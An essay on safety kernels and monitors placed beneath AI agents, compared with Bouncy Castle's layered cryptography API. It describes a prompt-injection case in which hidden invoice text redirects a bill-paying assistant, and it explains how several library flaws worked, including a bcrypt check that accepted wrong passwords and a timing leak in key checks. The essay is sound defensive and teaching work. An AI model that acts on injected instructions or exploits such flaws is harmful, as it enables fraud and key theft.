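# A small, non-learned safety kernel beneath AI components, compared with Bouncy Castle's light-weight API

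## The question, and what it means to check a program

A safety kernel is a small conventional program that sits between a larger system and whatever that system can affect. Every consequential action must pass through the kernel, which allows or refuses it by fixed rules. The idea grew out of operating-system security in the 1970s. Engineers later tried it on medical devices and reactors, whose software had become too large for anyone to check in full. It has a new use in AI systems for much the same reason. Programmers can read conventional code line by line and sometimes prove it correct, but nobody can read a language model's weights, the numbers that training produces, in that way.

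Could an AI system have two layers that need different amounts of trust? The lower layer would be a kernel that people can read, test and perhaps prove correct. The upper layer would contain AI components that could not do certain kinds of harm, even if they were mistaken or under an attacker's influence. Bouncy Castle, a cryptography library, offers a comparison because it keeps its algorithms in a plain low-level layer beneath a second layer that plugs them into Java's standard interface. How useful the comparison is depends on what "checked" means, and people use that word for at least five different activities.

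### An assistant that pays bills

A small company might let an AI assistant read its email and pay its suppliers' bills. When a supplier sends an invoice, the assistant picks out the payee, the amount and the account number, and a payment order goes to the bank. The language model that reads the invoice is a *learned component*, a part of the system whose behaviour comes from training on data rather than from rules that someone wrote.

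Now a stranger sends what looks like an invoice, but has added an instruction in white text on the white page to pay the outstanding balance into a new account. This is *prompt injection*, in which someone hides instructions in material that the assistant reads, and the assistant may follow them as if they came from its user. Improving the wording of the assistant's own instructions does not remove the problem. *Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) compares AI agents with operating systems and points out that a single model takes in an agent's standing instructions, the user's request and whatever files the agent opens, and cannot tell them apart.

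A kernel for this assistant would stand between it and the bank. The assistant could still propose any payment, but only the kernel would hold the bank credentials. The company might set three rules:

- Payments go only to accounts on a list that the bookkeeper keeps.
- No more than €5,000 leaves the company in a day.
- A person approves any single payment above €2,000.

These rules are the *policy*. The program that applies them is separate, and it can work flawlessly even if the bookkeeper's list contains a fraudster's account.

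*Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) puts this in mathematical form. Let s be the state of everything the rules depend on, here the approved accounts and the day's payments so far. A policy is a function Π that maps each state to Allow or Block. When the assistant requests an action t, the monitor holds the action back and computes the state that would follow, s′ = Δ(s, t). If Π(s′) is Block, the action never happens and the state stays at s. Suppose €4,200 has gone out today and the assistant requests another payment of €1,100. The projected total is €5,300, so the kernel refuses and the total stays at €4,200. The calculation does not include the model's reasons for requesting the payment, so an email that persuades the model does not affect the kernel's decision.

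### Anderson's three requirements

The US Air Force had this problem in the early 1970s, with people in place of models. It wanted users with different security clearances to share one computer, and some of those users could write and run their own programs. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) is the report of a panel of specialists who assumed that one of the users was an attacker. The panel recommended building on a *reference monitor*, which checks every attempt by a program to reach data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do.

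Anderson set three requirements for the checker. It must be tamper-proof, because otherwise an attacker can alter it. It must always be invoked, and any programs that escape the check become part of the security apparatus and have to meet the same standard. It must also be small enough for analysis and tests "the completeness of which can be assured", because otherwise nobody can know that it works in every case.

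The report applied these requirements to a commercial machine of the day, the HIS 635 with its operating system GCOS III. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory. But to read or write a file, the program had to call the operating system, most of which ran with the memory check switched off. Treating the operating system itself as the checker would not have met the requirements either, because it had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse, and test attacks on it had already succeeded.

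Anderson's three requirements also rule out replacing the kernel with a rule in the standing instructions of the company's assistant, such as "never pay an account that is not on the list". Li and colleagues audit such rules and find that they meet none of the requirements. The model may not follow them. Text in an email can override them, because the email and the rules arrive in the same input. Their effect also depends on a neural network whose behaviour nobody can inspect well enough to vouch for it.

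Anderson called the software part of such a checker a security kernel. In *Kernels for Safety?*, Rushby (1989) asked whether the same structure could provide safety as well as secrecy. He concluded, with qualifications, that it could, because a kernel can rigorously guarantee that certain "faults of commission" will not occur. In the company's case, a kernel can prevent a payment to a stranger but cannot ensure that the electricity bill gets paid.

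In *Generalized Implementation of Software Safety Policies*, Knight and Wika worked out what rules a safety kernel might have for real equipment. One of their two cases was an experimental device for brain surgery that uses six superconducting electromagnets to steer a small magnet through the patient's brain. They identified 42 rules for it. For example, the coil currents must go to zero if the magnet moves faster than 2.0 millimetres per second, and the total X-ray dose in an operation must stay below 100 millirem. The rules apply whatever causes the problem, whether a sensor, a programmer or the surgeon, so a short list can cover many faults.

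Knight and Wika also distinguished kernels in Rushby's sense, which enforce their rules regardless of what the application does, from designs called safety kernels that only offered protective services and relied on the application to use them properly. A payment-checking function that the assistant may call or skip is of the second, weaker kind, and it protects the company only if the model uses it properly.

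### What else has to work

A guarantee about the kernel depends on more than the kernel. The *trusted computing base* is everything that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold. In the US National Institute of Standards and Technology's glossary, *trusted computing base (TCB)* includes hardware and firmware as well as software.

A kernel of a few hundred lines can depend on a trusted computing base of millions of lines. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) describes a monitor for AI agents that run commands on a computer, and states which components are trusted. These are the host's operating-system kernel, the layer that traces the agent's system calls, the driver for the temporary file system in which commands first run, and the network proxy. They also include the monitor's own code for inferring from the system calls what the agent did, and the proof checker, compiler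 and runtime of Lean, the language in which the policies and proofs are written. The bill-paying kernel's trusted computing base would include the server's operating system, the code that reads the account number out of a payment order, the connection to the bank, and the file that holds the supplier list.

### Five ways to check a program

Anderson's requirement of smallness is ambiguous about what it means to check a program. The first volume of his report requires analysis and tests. The second, *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2* (1972), treats the same condition as equivalent to being capable of proof. Li and colleagues shorten the requirement to "verifiable" and grade it by whether someone can check the policy in advance. A vendor who advertises a "verified" kernel could mean any of these standards, or something weaker.

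A very small function helps to tell them apart. Ho, Fournet and colleagues (2026), in *Scaling Verification of Cryptographic Software with Aeneas, Rust, and Lean*, prove properties of code in SymCrypt, Microsoft's cryptographic library. One of their examples finds the remainder of a number x after division by 3,329, without dividing by 3,329. It works in three steps:

1. Multiply x by the constant 1,290,168, which is 2³² / 3,329 rounded up.
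2. Divide the product by 2³² and drop the fraction, which for a computer only means discarding 32 binary digits. The result is the quotient.
3. Subtract 3,329 times the quotient from x.

A *specification* is an exact statement of what a program must do. Here, for every x below 6,658, the function must finish without an error and return the remainder of x divided by 3,329.

If the programmer had rounded the constant down to 1,290,167, the function would be wrong for only one permitted input. Given x = 3,329, it would return 3,329 instead of 0.

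**Reading by experts.** A specialist who knows the trick might notice the wrong constant, or might not. Reading is the only one of the five methods that can turn up a problem nobody thought to look for, including a mistake in the specification itself. But a clean report proves little. Anderson made this complaint about "tiger teams", specialists who tested systems by trying to break into them. Their results depended on who was on the team, and a failed attack would not have shown whether the system was secure, though no team was known to have failed. Both problems also apply to reading code. OpenSSL, another cryptography library, has public source code, yet an incorrect change specific to the Debian version made its key material guessable (*An AI Approach to Verified Production Cryptographic Libraries*, 2026).

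**Testing against known answers.** The tester runs the program on inputs for which someone has published the right outputs. NIST requires such tests for Skipjack, an older cipher, including one that varies the ciphertext and another that varies the key. A pass shows that the program is right on those inputs. A hundred random inputs would expose the wrong constant about 1.5% of the time, while a tester who routinely tries boundary values would find it at once, so the result depends heavily on who picks the tests. A computer could also try all 6,658 inputs to this function in an instant, but a cipher with a 256-bit key has 2²⁵⁶ possible keys, far too many to try.

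**Certification by an accredited laboratory** means that an outside body tests the product against a fixed set of requirements. In the American programme for cryptographic modules, independent laboratories do the testing and NIST reviews what they submit; more than 1,000 validated modules are currently active. Certification makes the testing independent of the vendor, but it covers only the listed requirements. NIST warns that validation gives no assurance that a product uses the module inside it correctly. The same caveat would apply to a certified payment kernel, and the certificate would give no protection to a company that let the assistant reach the bank without going through the kernel.

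**Differential testing.** The tester feeds the same inputs to two implementations and looks for disagreements. Nobody has to know the right answers beforehand, so a machine can generate millions of cases. Comparing the fast remainder function with ordinary division would expose the wrong constant as soon as the tester tried 3,329. A disagreement proves that at least one of the programs is wrong, but agreement is weaker evidence because both programmers may have misread the standard in the same way. The method is still useful for checking a fast program against a slow one that has been proved correct. Sistla and colleagues suggest using it for systems busier than their prototype, to compare a fast version written in the programming language Rust with the Lean original.

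**Machine-checked proof.** Ho and colleagues state the specification of the remainder function as a theorem in Lean and prove it for every x below 6,658. A small core program in Lean checks each step, so it does not matter whether a person or an AI wrote the proof. If the constant were rounded down, the theorem would be false and Lean would accept no proof of it. The proof also shows that no intermediate step overflows, which is easy to forget to test. This kind of checking is usually called *formal verification*, and it is the only one of the five that covers all inputs when there are too many to try.

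It covers them only with respect to the theorem. Ho and colleagues still trust the compiler and the tools that translate Rust into Lean, and they do not prove that the code's running time leaks nothing about secret keys. They also test their specifications against official known answers, because an error in copying the standard would otherwise become part of the theorem. *The Prover Is the Judge* (2026), on security software that AI agents wrote together with its proofs, describes the remaining danger as "a correct proof of a wrong specification". *SoK* (2026), a survey of verification tools for zero-knowledge proofs, therefore counts the theorem statement as part of the trusted computing base.

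The bill-paying kernel could go wrong in this way. Its author might prove that, for every state and every request, the kernel lets a payment through only if the account is on the list and the day's total stays within €5,000. But suppose the specification counts only payments the bank has completed towards the day's total. Three payments of €1,900, each too small to need a person's approval, would all pass if sent within a minute, because none would have cleared when the kernel checked the others. The proof would still be valid, but the company would lose €5,700 despite the €5,000 limit.

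## How Bouncy Castle's two layers fit together

Bouncy Castle is open source and has versions for Java and C#. A few programmers released the first version in May 2000, and an Australian charity called the Legion of the Bouncy Castle now owns the code. In a post for the project's 25th anniversary, Bouncy Castle (2025) reported more than six million downloads a month.

In the Java version, the lower layer is called the *light-weight API*, and a program can call its classes directly. The upper layer is a *provider* for Java's cryptography interface, the JCA, and its extension for encryption, the JCE. Other organisations also write providers for the same interface.

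Suppose the company with the bill-paying assistant encrypts each 100-byte payment order before storing it. The order's reference number has to stay readable so that the bookkeeper can find the order, but the company wants to know if anyone has altered the number. AES-GCM, a common encryption method, can do both the encryption and the check, and a Java program can use it through either layer.

### What AES-GCM computes

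AES is a block cipher that uses a secret key to turn any 16-byte block B into another 16-byte block, E(B). Galois/Counter Mode (GCM) extends this to longer messages and adds a *tag*, a short value used to detect tampering. GCM also needs a *nonce* N, usually 12 bytes long, which must never repeat under the same key.

To encrypt block i of the message, Pᵢ, GCM joins the nonce to a 4-byte counter, encrypts the result and combines it with the message bit by bit:

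Cᵢ = Pᵢ ⊕ E(N ‖ i+1)

For the tag, let H be the encryption of a block of zeros, and start from X₀ = 0. GCM goes through the blocks Bⱼ of the readable data and then of the ciphertext, followed by one block that records their lengths, and computes

Xⱼ = (Xⱼ₋₁ ⊕ Bⱼ) · H

where the multiplication takes place in a finite field of 2¹²⁸ elements. The last X, combined with E(N ‖ 1), is the tag. If someone changes a digit of the reference number, the recomputed tag will not match.

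AES appears in these formulas only as E, so the code for GCM does not depend on how AES works inside. Bouncy Castle's developers therefore put the two in separate classes.

### Calling the light-weight classes

With error handling left out, the direct route takes five lines:

```java
GCMModeCipher gcm = GCMBlockCipher.newInstance(new AESEngine());
gcm.init(true, new AEADParameters(new KeyParameter(key), 128, nonce, reference));
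byte[] out = new byte[gcm.getOutputSize(order.length)];
int n = gcm.processBytes(order, 0, order.length, out, 0);
gcm.doFinal(out, n);
```

The first line places an AES engine inside a GCM object. The second passes the key, the tag length in bits, the nonce and the readable reference number, in the order given in Bouncy Castle's *Class AEADParameters*. `true` means encrypt. For a 100-byte order, `getOutputSize` returns 116, because a 16-byte tag will follow the ciphertext. `processBytes` then encrypts the six complete blocks, and `doFinal` encrypts the last four bytes and adds the tag. When decrypting, `doFinal` checks the tag and raises an error if it is wrong.

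The caller of the light-weight API chooses every setting and can choose weak ones. According to Bouncy Castle's *Class GCMBlockCipher*, a tag may be as short as 32 bits, although the developers advise against anything below 96. A random forgery has one chance in about 4.3 billion of matching a 32-bit tag, which is weak protection against an attacker who can make many attempts. The class rejects invalid settings, but it does not check whether this program should be encrypting this order.

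Real applications use the lower layer this way. For Spring Security, a framework that handles logins and encryption in Java applications, Tran wrote an encryptor that calls the AES and GCM classes directly and gives the same result as the standard interface. But a program that names a library's internal classes has to be updated when the developers replace them. Tran's code names a particular AES class, `AESFastEngine`, and includes an annotation to silence the compiler's warnings about outdated code. Bouncy Castle's developers have since marked the GCM constructor it calls as outdated too.

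### Going through the provider

The same encryption through Java's interface looks like this:

```java
Security.addProvider(new BouncyCastleProvider());
Cipher cipher = Cipher.getInstance("AES/GCM/NoPadding", "BC");
cipher.init(Cipher.ENCRYPT_MODE, new SecretKeySpec(key, "AES"),
            new GCMParameterSpec(128, nonce));
cipher.updateAAD(reference);
byte[] out = cipher.doFinal(order);
```

The first line adds Bouncy Castle to Java's list of providers. The second requests a cipher by name. According to Java's *Class Cipher*, the name describes the operation, and the program may also name a provider, here "BC". The returned `Cipher` object belongs to Java. It wraps a Bouncy Castle object built on `CipherSpi`, a template that every cipher provider must follow.

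In Bouncy Castle's *Specifications*, the developers describe the provider as "a wrapper built on top of the light-weight API". Its source code bears them out. In release 1.61, Bouncy Castle had a ready-made provider class for AES-GCM whose constructor contained a single statement:

```java
super(new GCMBlockCipher(new AESEngine()));
```

So the same two classes as before do the arithmetic, and the provider's own code handles everything else. With the same key, nonce, reference and order, both routes produce the same 116 bytes.

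Much of that is names. The provider's AES file registers "AES" and a long list of numerical identifiers that stand for AES in certificates and encrypted messages. Three of the identifiers are wrong because of a typo in an early document. They ended up in real messages, so the provider accepts them when reading but never writes them, according to a comment in the file. When a program asks for "AES/GCM/NoPadding", Java finds the entry for AES and switches the object it refers to into GCM mode. A program that asks only for "AES" gets ECB mode, which encrypts each block separately, so identical blocks of a message produce identical ciphertext. The provider sets that default, so someone who reviewed only the AES and GCM classes would miss it.

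The provider also converts objects. The light-weight classes take the key as raw bytes in a `KeyParameter`, while Java programs pass standard key objects, which might come from a key file or another library. The GCM settings need converting too. Java counts the tag length in bits, but the standard format for storing the settings with an encrypted message counts it in bytes, so Bouncy Castle has a helper that multiplies or divides by eight. A mistake in that helper could give a message the wrong tag length even if the AES and GCM code were correct. When a bad tag raises one of Bouncy Castle's own exceptions in the lower layer, the provider turns it into the exception that Java programs expect.

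Bouncy Castle's developers call this surrounding code "scaffolding" in slides about getting the library certified, and argue that users depend on it as much as on the algorithms. The bill-paying kernel would also need scaffolding to read payment orders, and a proof of the kernel's rules alone would not cover that code.

### Why there are two layers

The lower layer came first. Bouncy Castle's developers recall in *Open Source Development and Sustainability* that one of them was experimenting with J2ME, the edition of Java for small devices such as mobile phones. They wrote a low-level API for it and then built a provider on top. J2ME did not include the JCE, so a provider would have had nothing to plug into there. Bouncy Castle still lists a J2ME release that contains only the light-weight API.

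Another reason was applets, small Java programs that a web browser downloaded and ran as part of a page. An applet's author could include the light-weight classes in the download, but had no easy way to install a provider on each visitor's computer. In some older versions of Java, a provider worked only from a directory inside the Java installation.

To comply with American export rules, Java came with policy files that capped the length of keys, at 128 bits for AES. A program that asked for a 256-bit key got the error "Unsupported keysize or algorithm parameters" until the user installed different policy files. Java's own `Cipher` class raised the error, so changing the provider did not help. The cap did not affect the light-weight classes, which were ordinary Java code that did not use `Cipher`. Java 9 switched the cap off by default in 2017.

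The cap resembled a safety kernel in some ways. Its policy was fixed and kept in a file separate from the program that applied it, and Java checked each request at a single point. But it failed Anderson's requirement that the checker must always be invoked, because a program could do the same arithmetic with other code. No checker inside Java could have prevented that, since anyone can implement AES from its published description. A kernel can block a payment, however, because the bank requires credentials that only the kernel holds. A kernel can therefore control access to something outside the AI system much more reliably than it can control what the system computes.

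### What "drop-in" means

A provider is a *drop-in* replacement for another if an application can switch to it without a rewrite. In the provider example above, only the first line and the name "BC" tie the program to Bouncy Castle. Without them, Java would go down its list of providers and use the first that offered AES-GCM. An administrator can change the provider without touching the application by setting the order of that list in a configuration file. In their specifications, Bouncy Castle's developers give the example of a company that wants to move its cryptography to special hardware.

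Such a switch can still go wrong. The new provider has to offer the same algorithms and behave as the application expects, including in undocumented ways. The developers' slides on certification mention software from other companies that relied on undocumented behaviour and could not use a library that lacked it. A program is also tied to Bouncy Castle if it uses an algorithm that is available only through the light-weight API. The Bouncy Castle repository's README names several, including J-PAKE, which lets two parties who share a password agree on a key.

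When a company replaces Bouncy Castle's provider, it also removes the light-weight classes under it and keeps only Java's interface. A safety kernel would need the opposite arrangement, because the company would want to replace the language model, perhaps every few months, and keep the kernel underneath unchanged. Bouncy Castle's certified edition, which follows the American FIPS standard, is even further from that arrangement because its provider is largely a drop-in replacement for the regular one, but its low-level API is quite different.

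### The modules and what depends on what

The developers divide the source code into modules. These are the main ones:

| Module | What it contains |
|---|---|
| core | The light-weight API |
| prov | The providers for Java's cryptography interface |
| util | Shared code, mostly for the data format that certificates use |
| pkix | Certificates, signed and encrypted messages, timestamps |
| pg | OpenPGP, a standard for encrypting email and files |
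| tls | TLS, the protocol that secures web connections |

The provider layer depends on the core module, not the reverse. A provider class may import from both Java's cryptography API and the light-weight API. The AES file, for example, takes Java's standard parameter classes from `javax.crypto` and the algorithms from `org.bouncycastle.crypto`. A light-weight class cannot use `javax.crypto`, because it must run on J2ME. This restriction also helps reviewers, who can follow an encryption through the core module without understanding how Java finds and loads providers.

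The developers publish both layers, core and prov, in a single file called `bcprov`, which every other module requires. The build can produce a separate file for core, but they do not publish it on Maven Central, the site from which most Java projects fetch their libraries. A program that only encrypts payment orders therefore receives all the algorithms and both providers, the regular one and one for post-quantum algorithms, which are meant to withstand attack by quantum computers. The boundary between the layers helps programmers organise the code, but a program can still call any public class in either one.

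### How thin the lower layer is

In a message to users, Hook (2010), in *Celebrate 10 years of BouncyCastle*, put the first release at about 24,000 lines of Java; the project's later slides give 27,000. Either would have been a manageable amount for a small team to read. The library has grown a great deal since, though people have counted it in different ways:

| Release | Lines of Java | What the count covers |
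|---|---|---|
| First, 2000 | about 27,000 | Library and tests |
| 1.44 | 277,890 | Debian's source package |
| 1.53 | 390,640 | Library and tests |
| 1.56 | 556,128 | Debian's source package |
| 1.72 | 855,832 | Debian's source package |
| 1.80 | 968,332 | Debian's source package |

Debian, a version of Linux, packages the library for its users. Its source package includes tests and extra code for old editions of Java, which probably explains much of the jump between releases 1.53 and 1.56. Within Debian's series, the total grew about three and a half times from 1.44 to 1.80.

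These totals cover all the modules, including tests and compatibility code, so they overstate the size of the lower layer. According to the developers' certification slides, the library proper had 324,000 of the 565,000 lines at that time. If the proportion were the same in release 1.80, the library proper would have about 555,000 lines, which would include the provider, certificates, OpenPGP and TLS as well as core.

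Even so, core is large. The specifications list 38 engines in the light-weight API's table of block ciphers, including variants that encrypt other keys, along with 12 stream ciphers and 37 hash functions. Core also includes signatures, key agreement, password hashing and a growing set of post-quantum algorithms. Some of these support old data or particular national standards, and most applications will never use them. "Light-weight" refers to how little the API needs from the Java system around it, not to the amount of code. The whole layer is much too large to meet Anderson's requirement of smallness.

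To follow a single operation, such as the encryption of the payment order, a reviewer would need to read only the AES engine, the GCM class and the code for its multiplication, the objects that carry the key and settings, and a few helper classes. One specialist could realistically do this. Likewise, the developers of a kernel that used Bouncy Castle to check signatures on payment orders could review the classes the kernel calls and leave the rest of the library out of the program.

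They would have to repeat the review when those classes changed. The *bouncy Castle Java* page on Open Hub, a site that tracks activity in open-source projects, shows 3,934 changes by 24 contributors in the year to October 2026, 57% more changes than in the year before. Most probably had nothing to do with AES-GCM, but someone has to check each new release for any that did.

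## What checking the light-weight API has had, and what it missed

Most checks of Bouncy Castle's light-weight API run it on inputs with known answers. Anyone can also read the source, and outside researchers have proved some of the algorithm classes correct. These checks have worked well for each algorithm's core arithmetic, but much less well for the surrounding code that decides whether to accept a password, a signature or a number sent by a stranger. A payment kernel would consist mostly of code that makes such decisions.

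### Tests with known answers

Bouncy Castle's test programs run the light-weight classes on published worked examples like those in the AES standard. In one AES example, encrypting the block `00112233445566778899aabbccddeeff` with the key `000102030405060708090a0b0c0d0e0f` must produce `69c4e0d86a7b0430d8cdb78070b4c55a`.

Even a single example is good evidence that an AES implementation is correct, because AES puts each block through at least ten rounds of mixing, and a mistake in any round would change nearly every output. In NIST's Monte Carlo test for AES, each output feeds into the next encryption, 100,000 times in all, so one wrong bit along the way makes the final output wrong. Such tests find real mistakes. *Verification of Elliptic Curve Cryptography* (Hendrix, 2012) quotes NIST's annual report for 2008, which said that 27% of the algorithms and 48% of the modules that vendors submitted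 had security flaws, which the vendors then corrected.

Tests can miss rare errors. Hendrix describes one in OpenSSL's elliptic-curve arithmetic that affected fewer than one input in 2²⁹ (about 537 million). When it was discovered in 2007, nobody knew how to exploit it, but five years later researchers used it to recover complete keys. More tests would not solve the problem in general because, as Smith (2011) points out in *Axe*, if a cipher had few enough inputs for a tester to try them all, an attacker could do the same.

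Wycheproof, a set of tests that Google engineers published in 2016, focuses on mistakes that programmers often make in cryptography. It includes signatures with malformed encodings and public keys that do not lie on the right curve, and correct code should reject many of its cases. The Java tests call Bouncy Castle through Java's standard interface, so they reach the light-weight classes only where Bouncy Castle's provider uses them. For RSA signatures the provider has its own copy of the checking code, which was correct when the light-weight API's copy was found to be wrong in 2026.

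### What FIPS validation covers

Laboratories in the American certification programme apply the FIPS 140 standard. A module must first pass NIST's algorithm tests. Among other things, it must also have a documented boundary, test its own algorithms and stop working if a self-test fails. Smith notes that NIST itself admits that certification is not a proof.

Bouncy Castle's certificates belong to its FIPS edition and do not cover the light-weight API in the ordinary edition. Both editions come from the same developers and offer many of the same algorithms, but their low-level APIs differ so much that a programmer who calls `AESEngine` and `GCMBlockCipher` directly would have to rewrite that code for the FIPS edition.

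The editions do share some flaws. Debian's *bouncycastle* page lists the library's known security problems, including the 32 that release 1.85 fixed in July 2026. Nine of those were also in `bc-fips`, the main module of the certified edition. One concerned CCM, an encryption mode that, like GCM, adds a tag to each message. When decrypting, the code wrote the plaintext into the caller's memory before checking the tag. If the tag was wrong, the caller got an error, but the unverified plaintext stayed in memory, where an attacker might find it.

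The certified edition of Bouncy Castle needed a patch release, 2.1.1, to fix at least three flaws in version 2.1.0. Validation applies only to a particular version, so until the patched version is validated, a company has to choose between a certified module with a known flaw and a repaired one without a certificate.

### Proofs of individual algorithms

Formal proofs of some Bouncy Castle code do exist. Smith, then a doctoral student at Stanford, built a tool called Axe that proves two programs give the same output for every permitted input. One program is the Java code and the other can be a formal specification. For `AESFastEngine`, the most heavily optimised of Bouncy Castle's three AES classes at the time, the proof for encryption with a 128-bit key went as follows:

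1. Axe replaced each loop with as many copies of its contents as the loop had passes. This turned the Java code into a formula with 1,990 parts, and the specification into one with 2,729.
2. It joined the formulas into an equation and broke that down into operations on single bits, which gave 20,611 parts.
3. It tried random inputs and noted 3,684 sets of intermediate results that seemed always to be equal.
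4. Starting with the smallest, it proved these equalities, with 1,152 calls to an automatic solver, and merged the equal parts until the two final outputs were the same.

This took 83 seconds and covered all 2²⁵⁶ combinations of key and block. Smith did the same for decryption and for longer keys, and applied Axe to nine other algorithms in the light-weight API:

| Algorithm | What the proofs cover |
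|---|---|
| AES, three classes | Encryption and decryption, all three key lengths |
| DES, Triple DES, Skipjack | The block cipher |
| RC6 | Encryption and decryption, all three key lengths |
| RC2 | 64-bit keys only |
| Blowfish | 64-bit and 448-bit keys only |
| RC4 | Messages of any length that fits in a Java array |
| MD5, SHA-1 | Messages of any length that fits in a Java array |

The MD5 proof covers slightly altered code. Smith changed a `>` to a `>=` to make the proof easier, but noted that the original was probably not a bug.

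These proofs cover a small part of the light-weight API, and several of the algorithms in that part are now obsolete. GCM has no proof. If the company with the bill-paying assistant had encrypted its payment orders with Bouncy Castle's GCM in 2011, the proofs would have covered the AES step but not the code that produces and checks the tag. The proofs also assume that a program calls each class's methods in the usual order. They do not cover running time, and Smith warns that code with a proof may still leak its key through timing.

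`AESFastEngine` had that weakness. It uses large lookup tables for speed, and the entries it reads depend on the key, so an attacker who can observe the processor's memory accesses can learn about the key. In 2016 Bouncy Castle's developers replaced it with `AESEngine` as the provider's main AES class. They also changed `AESEngine` to remove a smaller leak, so Smith's proof for `AESEngine` applies to an earlier version of the code.

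Others have verified parts of the library too. Hendrix reports that Galois, an American company that makes verification tools, automatically verified the 817 lines of `AESFastEngine` for 128-bit keys in 40 minutes. In *Constructing Semantic Models of Programs with The Software Analysis Workbench*, Dockins, Foltzer and colleagues compare Bouncy Castle's SHA-384 hash function with a specification and a C version. Their proof covers only the inner loop of the compression function, which mixes one block of the message into the hash.

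### A password check that accepted wrong passwords

In March 2020, Bouncy Castle's developers released version 1.65 with a mistake in `OpenBSDBCrypt`, a core-module class that checks passwords. Black Duck, a software-security company, found the mistake that autumn. It is now listed in the public catalogue of security flaws as CVE-2020-28052.

A website that uses bcrypt does not store a user's password. It stores a 60-character string made up of a header such as `$2a$10$`, 22 characters of random salt and 31 characters of hash. When someone logs in, the class takes the password they typed, computes a new string with the same header and salt, and compares it with the stored one. In release 1.65 it did so by running this line for every i from 0 to 59:

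```java
isEqual &= (bcryptString.indexOf(i) == newBcryptString.indexOf(i));
```

The code should have called `charAt(i)`, which returns the character at position i. It called `indexOf(i)` instead, which treats i as a character code and returns the first position where that character occurs, or −1 if there is none. Codes 0 to 59 include the digits, the dollar sign, the full stop and the slash, but no letters. The check therefore ignored letters and looked only at the first occurrence of each digit.

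Suppose three strings differ only in their last six characters, and none has a 7 before that:

| String | Last six characters | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Stored | `kQ7xaB` | |
| From one wrong password | `mT7pcZ` | Accepted, because the first 7 is in the same place |
| From another wrong password | `m7TpcZ` | Rejected, because the first 7 is one place earlier |

How often the check would accept a wrong password depends on the characters in the stored string. Bcrypt writes its hashes in 64 characters, of which 52 are letters, and the letters cannot expose a wrong password. Neither can the digits 0, 1 and 2, because the header `$2a$10$` is the same in both strings and already contains them. Only the digits 3 to 9, the full stop and the slash can expose one. If the stored string contains none of these nine characters, the check accepts any wrong password whose own 31-character hash contains none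 of them either. By a rough calculation, the chance of that is about (55/64)³¹, or one in 110. If the salt contains all nine, the check accepts every password.

Black Duck's researchers bypassed 20% of the passwords they tested within 1,000 attempts, and found that, in rare cases, any input would work. They also concluded that an attacker could bypass every password with enough attempts.

An ordinary test would probably have missed the mistake. The right password always worked, and for 80% of the passwords in the experiments, 1,000 wrong ones in a row were all rejected, so a test that tried one or two wrong passwords would nearly always have passed. The source was public and a careful reader of the line could have spotted the problem, but the flaw lasted from March until the developers fixed it in release 1.67 on 1 November. Trying to prove the code correct would have exposed it, because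 the specification is simple (accept only if the strings are equal) and `mT7pcZ` is a counterexample.

The loop always ran to the end, which the programmer may have intended as a precaution. An ordinary comparison of two strings stops at the first difference, so an attacker can learn from the time it takes how much of a guess was right.

### Correct output and leaked keys

FrodoKEM, a post-quantum algorithm in the core module, shows why programmers take that precaution. It lets two computers agree on a secret key. One computer encrypts a random value with the other's public key. The receiver decrypts the value, encrypts it again and checks whether the result matches the ciphertext it received. If it doesn't match, the receiver continues with a meaningless key, so that the sender learns nothing from a tampered message.

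In Bouncy Castle's `FrodoEngine`, the time this check took depended on the data. According to Red Hat (2026), which makes a widely used version of Linux, the flaw (CVE-2026-5598) could leak private keys to an attacker over the network. Keyfactor, which provides support for Bouncy Castle, lists it among the flaws fixed in release 1.84.

If a comparison stops at the first mismatch, an attacker can take a valid ciphertext and slightly change a number near its end. FrodoKEM tolerates small errors, so the receiver may still recover the original random value. The second encryption then matches the ciphertext up to the altered number, and the comparison runs almost to the end. If the change is a little too large, the receiver recovers a different value, the second encryption looks nothing like the ciphertext and the comparison stops at once. The size of change at which the receiver starts to recover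 a different value depends on the private key, so an attacker who measures it for enough ciphertexts can work out the key. Red Hat notes that this typically takes many requests and a statistical analysis of the timings.

The check could give the right answer every time and still leak the key. Neither a known-answer test nor a proof like Smith's would detect the leak, because both cover only the output.

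Timing leaks also affected algorithms other than FrodoKEM. Release 1.86, which Bouncy Castle dates to 11 September 2026, fixed leaks in RSA, ECDSA and Diffie-Hellman, three of the most widely used algorithms in cryptography, and in several post-quantum ones. A payment kernel would be less exposed in one respect, because its list of approved accounts need not be secret and it would matter little if an attacker could time a lookup. Timing would still matter wherever the kernel handled the bank credentials or a signing key.

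### The 32 flaws fixed in release 1.85

Release 1.85 came out on 28 July 2026, according to Coopersmith (2026), in *Bouncy Castle 1.85 release fixes 32 CVEs*. Keyfactor's *CVE summaries* rate four of the flaws critical, 22 high and six medium. The summaries name the classes or features at fault but not always the module, so the counts below follow from where that code sits in the library:

| Module | Flaws | One of them |
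|---|---|---|
| core | 10 | RSA signature check skips two bytes |
| prov | 6 | Revoked certificate accepted as valid |
| pkix | 5 | Message with no signatures passes the signature check |
| pg | 5 | Shortened OpenPGP message accepted as complete |
| tls | 2 | Tiny network messages exhaust the memory |
| mls, for encrypted group chats | 2 | One member can stall all the others |
| mail, for signed and encrypted email | 1 | Signer can backdate a signature |
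| util | 1 | Nested message crashes the program |

Ten flaws were in the core and 22 were in the layers above it. Two of the ten are less certain to belong in the core than the others. One is in the rules that limit which names a certificate authority may certify, and the other is in reading data of a declared length. The totals do not show that the core is safer per line of code, because they do not account for how much code each module contains or how closely anyone had examined it.

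Four of the ten core flaws let an attacker crash or stall a program with specially made data. The other six weakened a security check or exposed secret information. None of the ten would have stopped two honest users of Bouncy Castle from exchanging messages, which helps explain why ordinary testing missed them.

The RSA flaw is an example of a mistake in a rarely used branch. An RSA signature contains a hash of the signed message, and the code that checks the signature must compare every byte of that hash. `RSADigestSigner` also accepts a variant encoding that leaves out an optional field, and for that variant it skipped the last two bytes of the hash. With a 32-byte hash, a forger would have needed about 2²⁴⁰ attempts to find a matching message instead of 2²⁵⁶. Both are infeasible, so the practical danger was smaller than the severity score of 8.7 out of 10 suggests. Differential testing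 within the library could have found the mistake by giving the same damaged signatures to the light-weight class and to the provider's copy.

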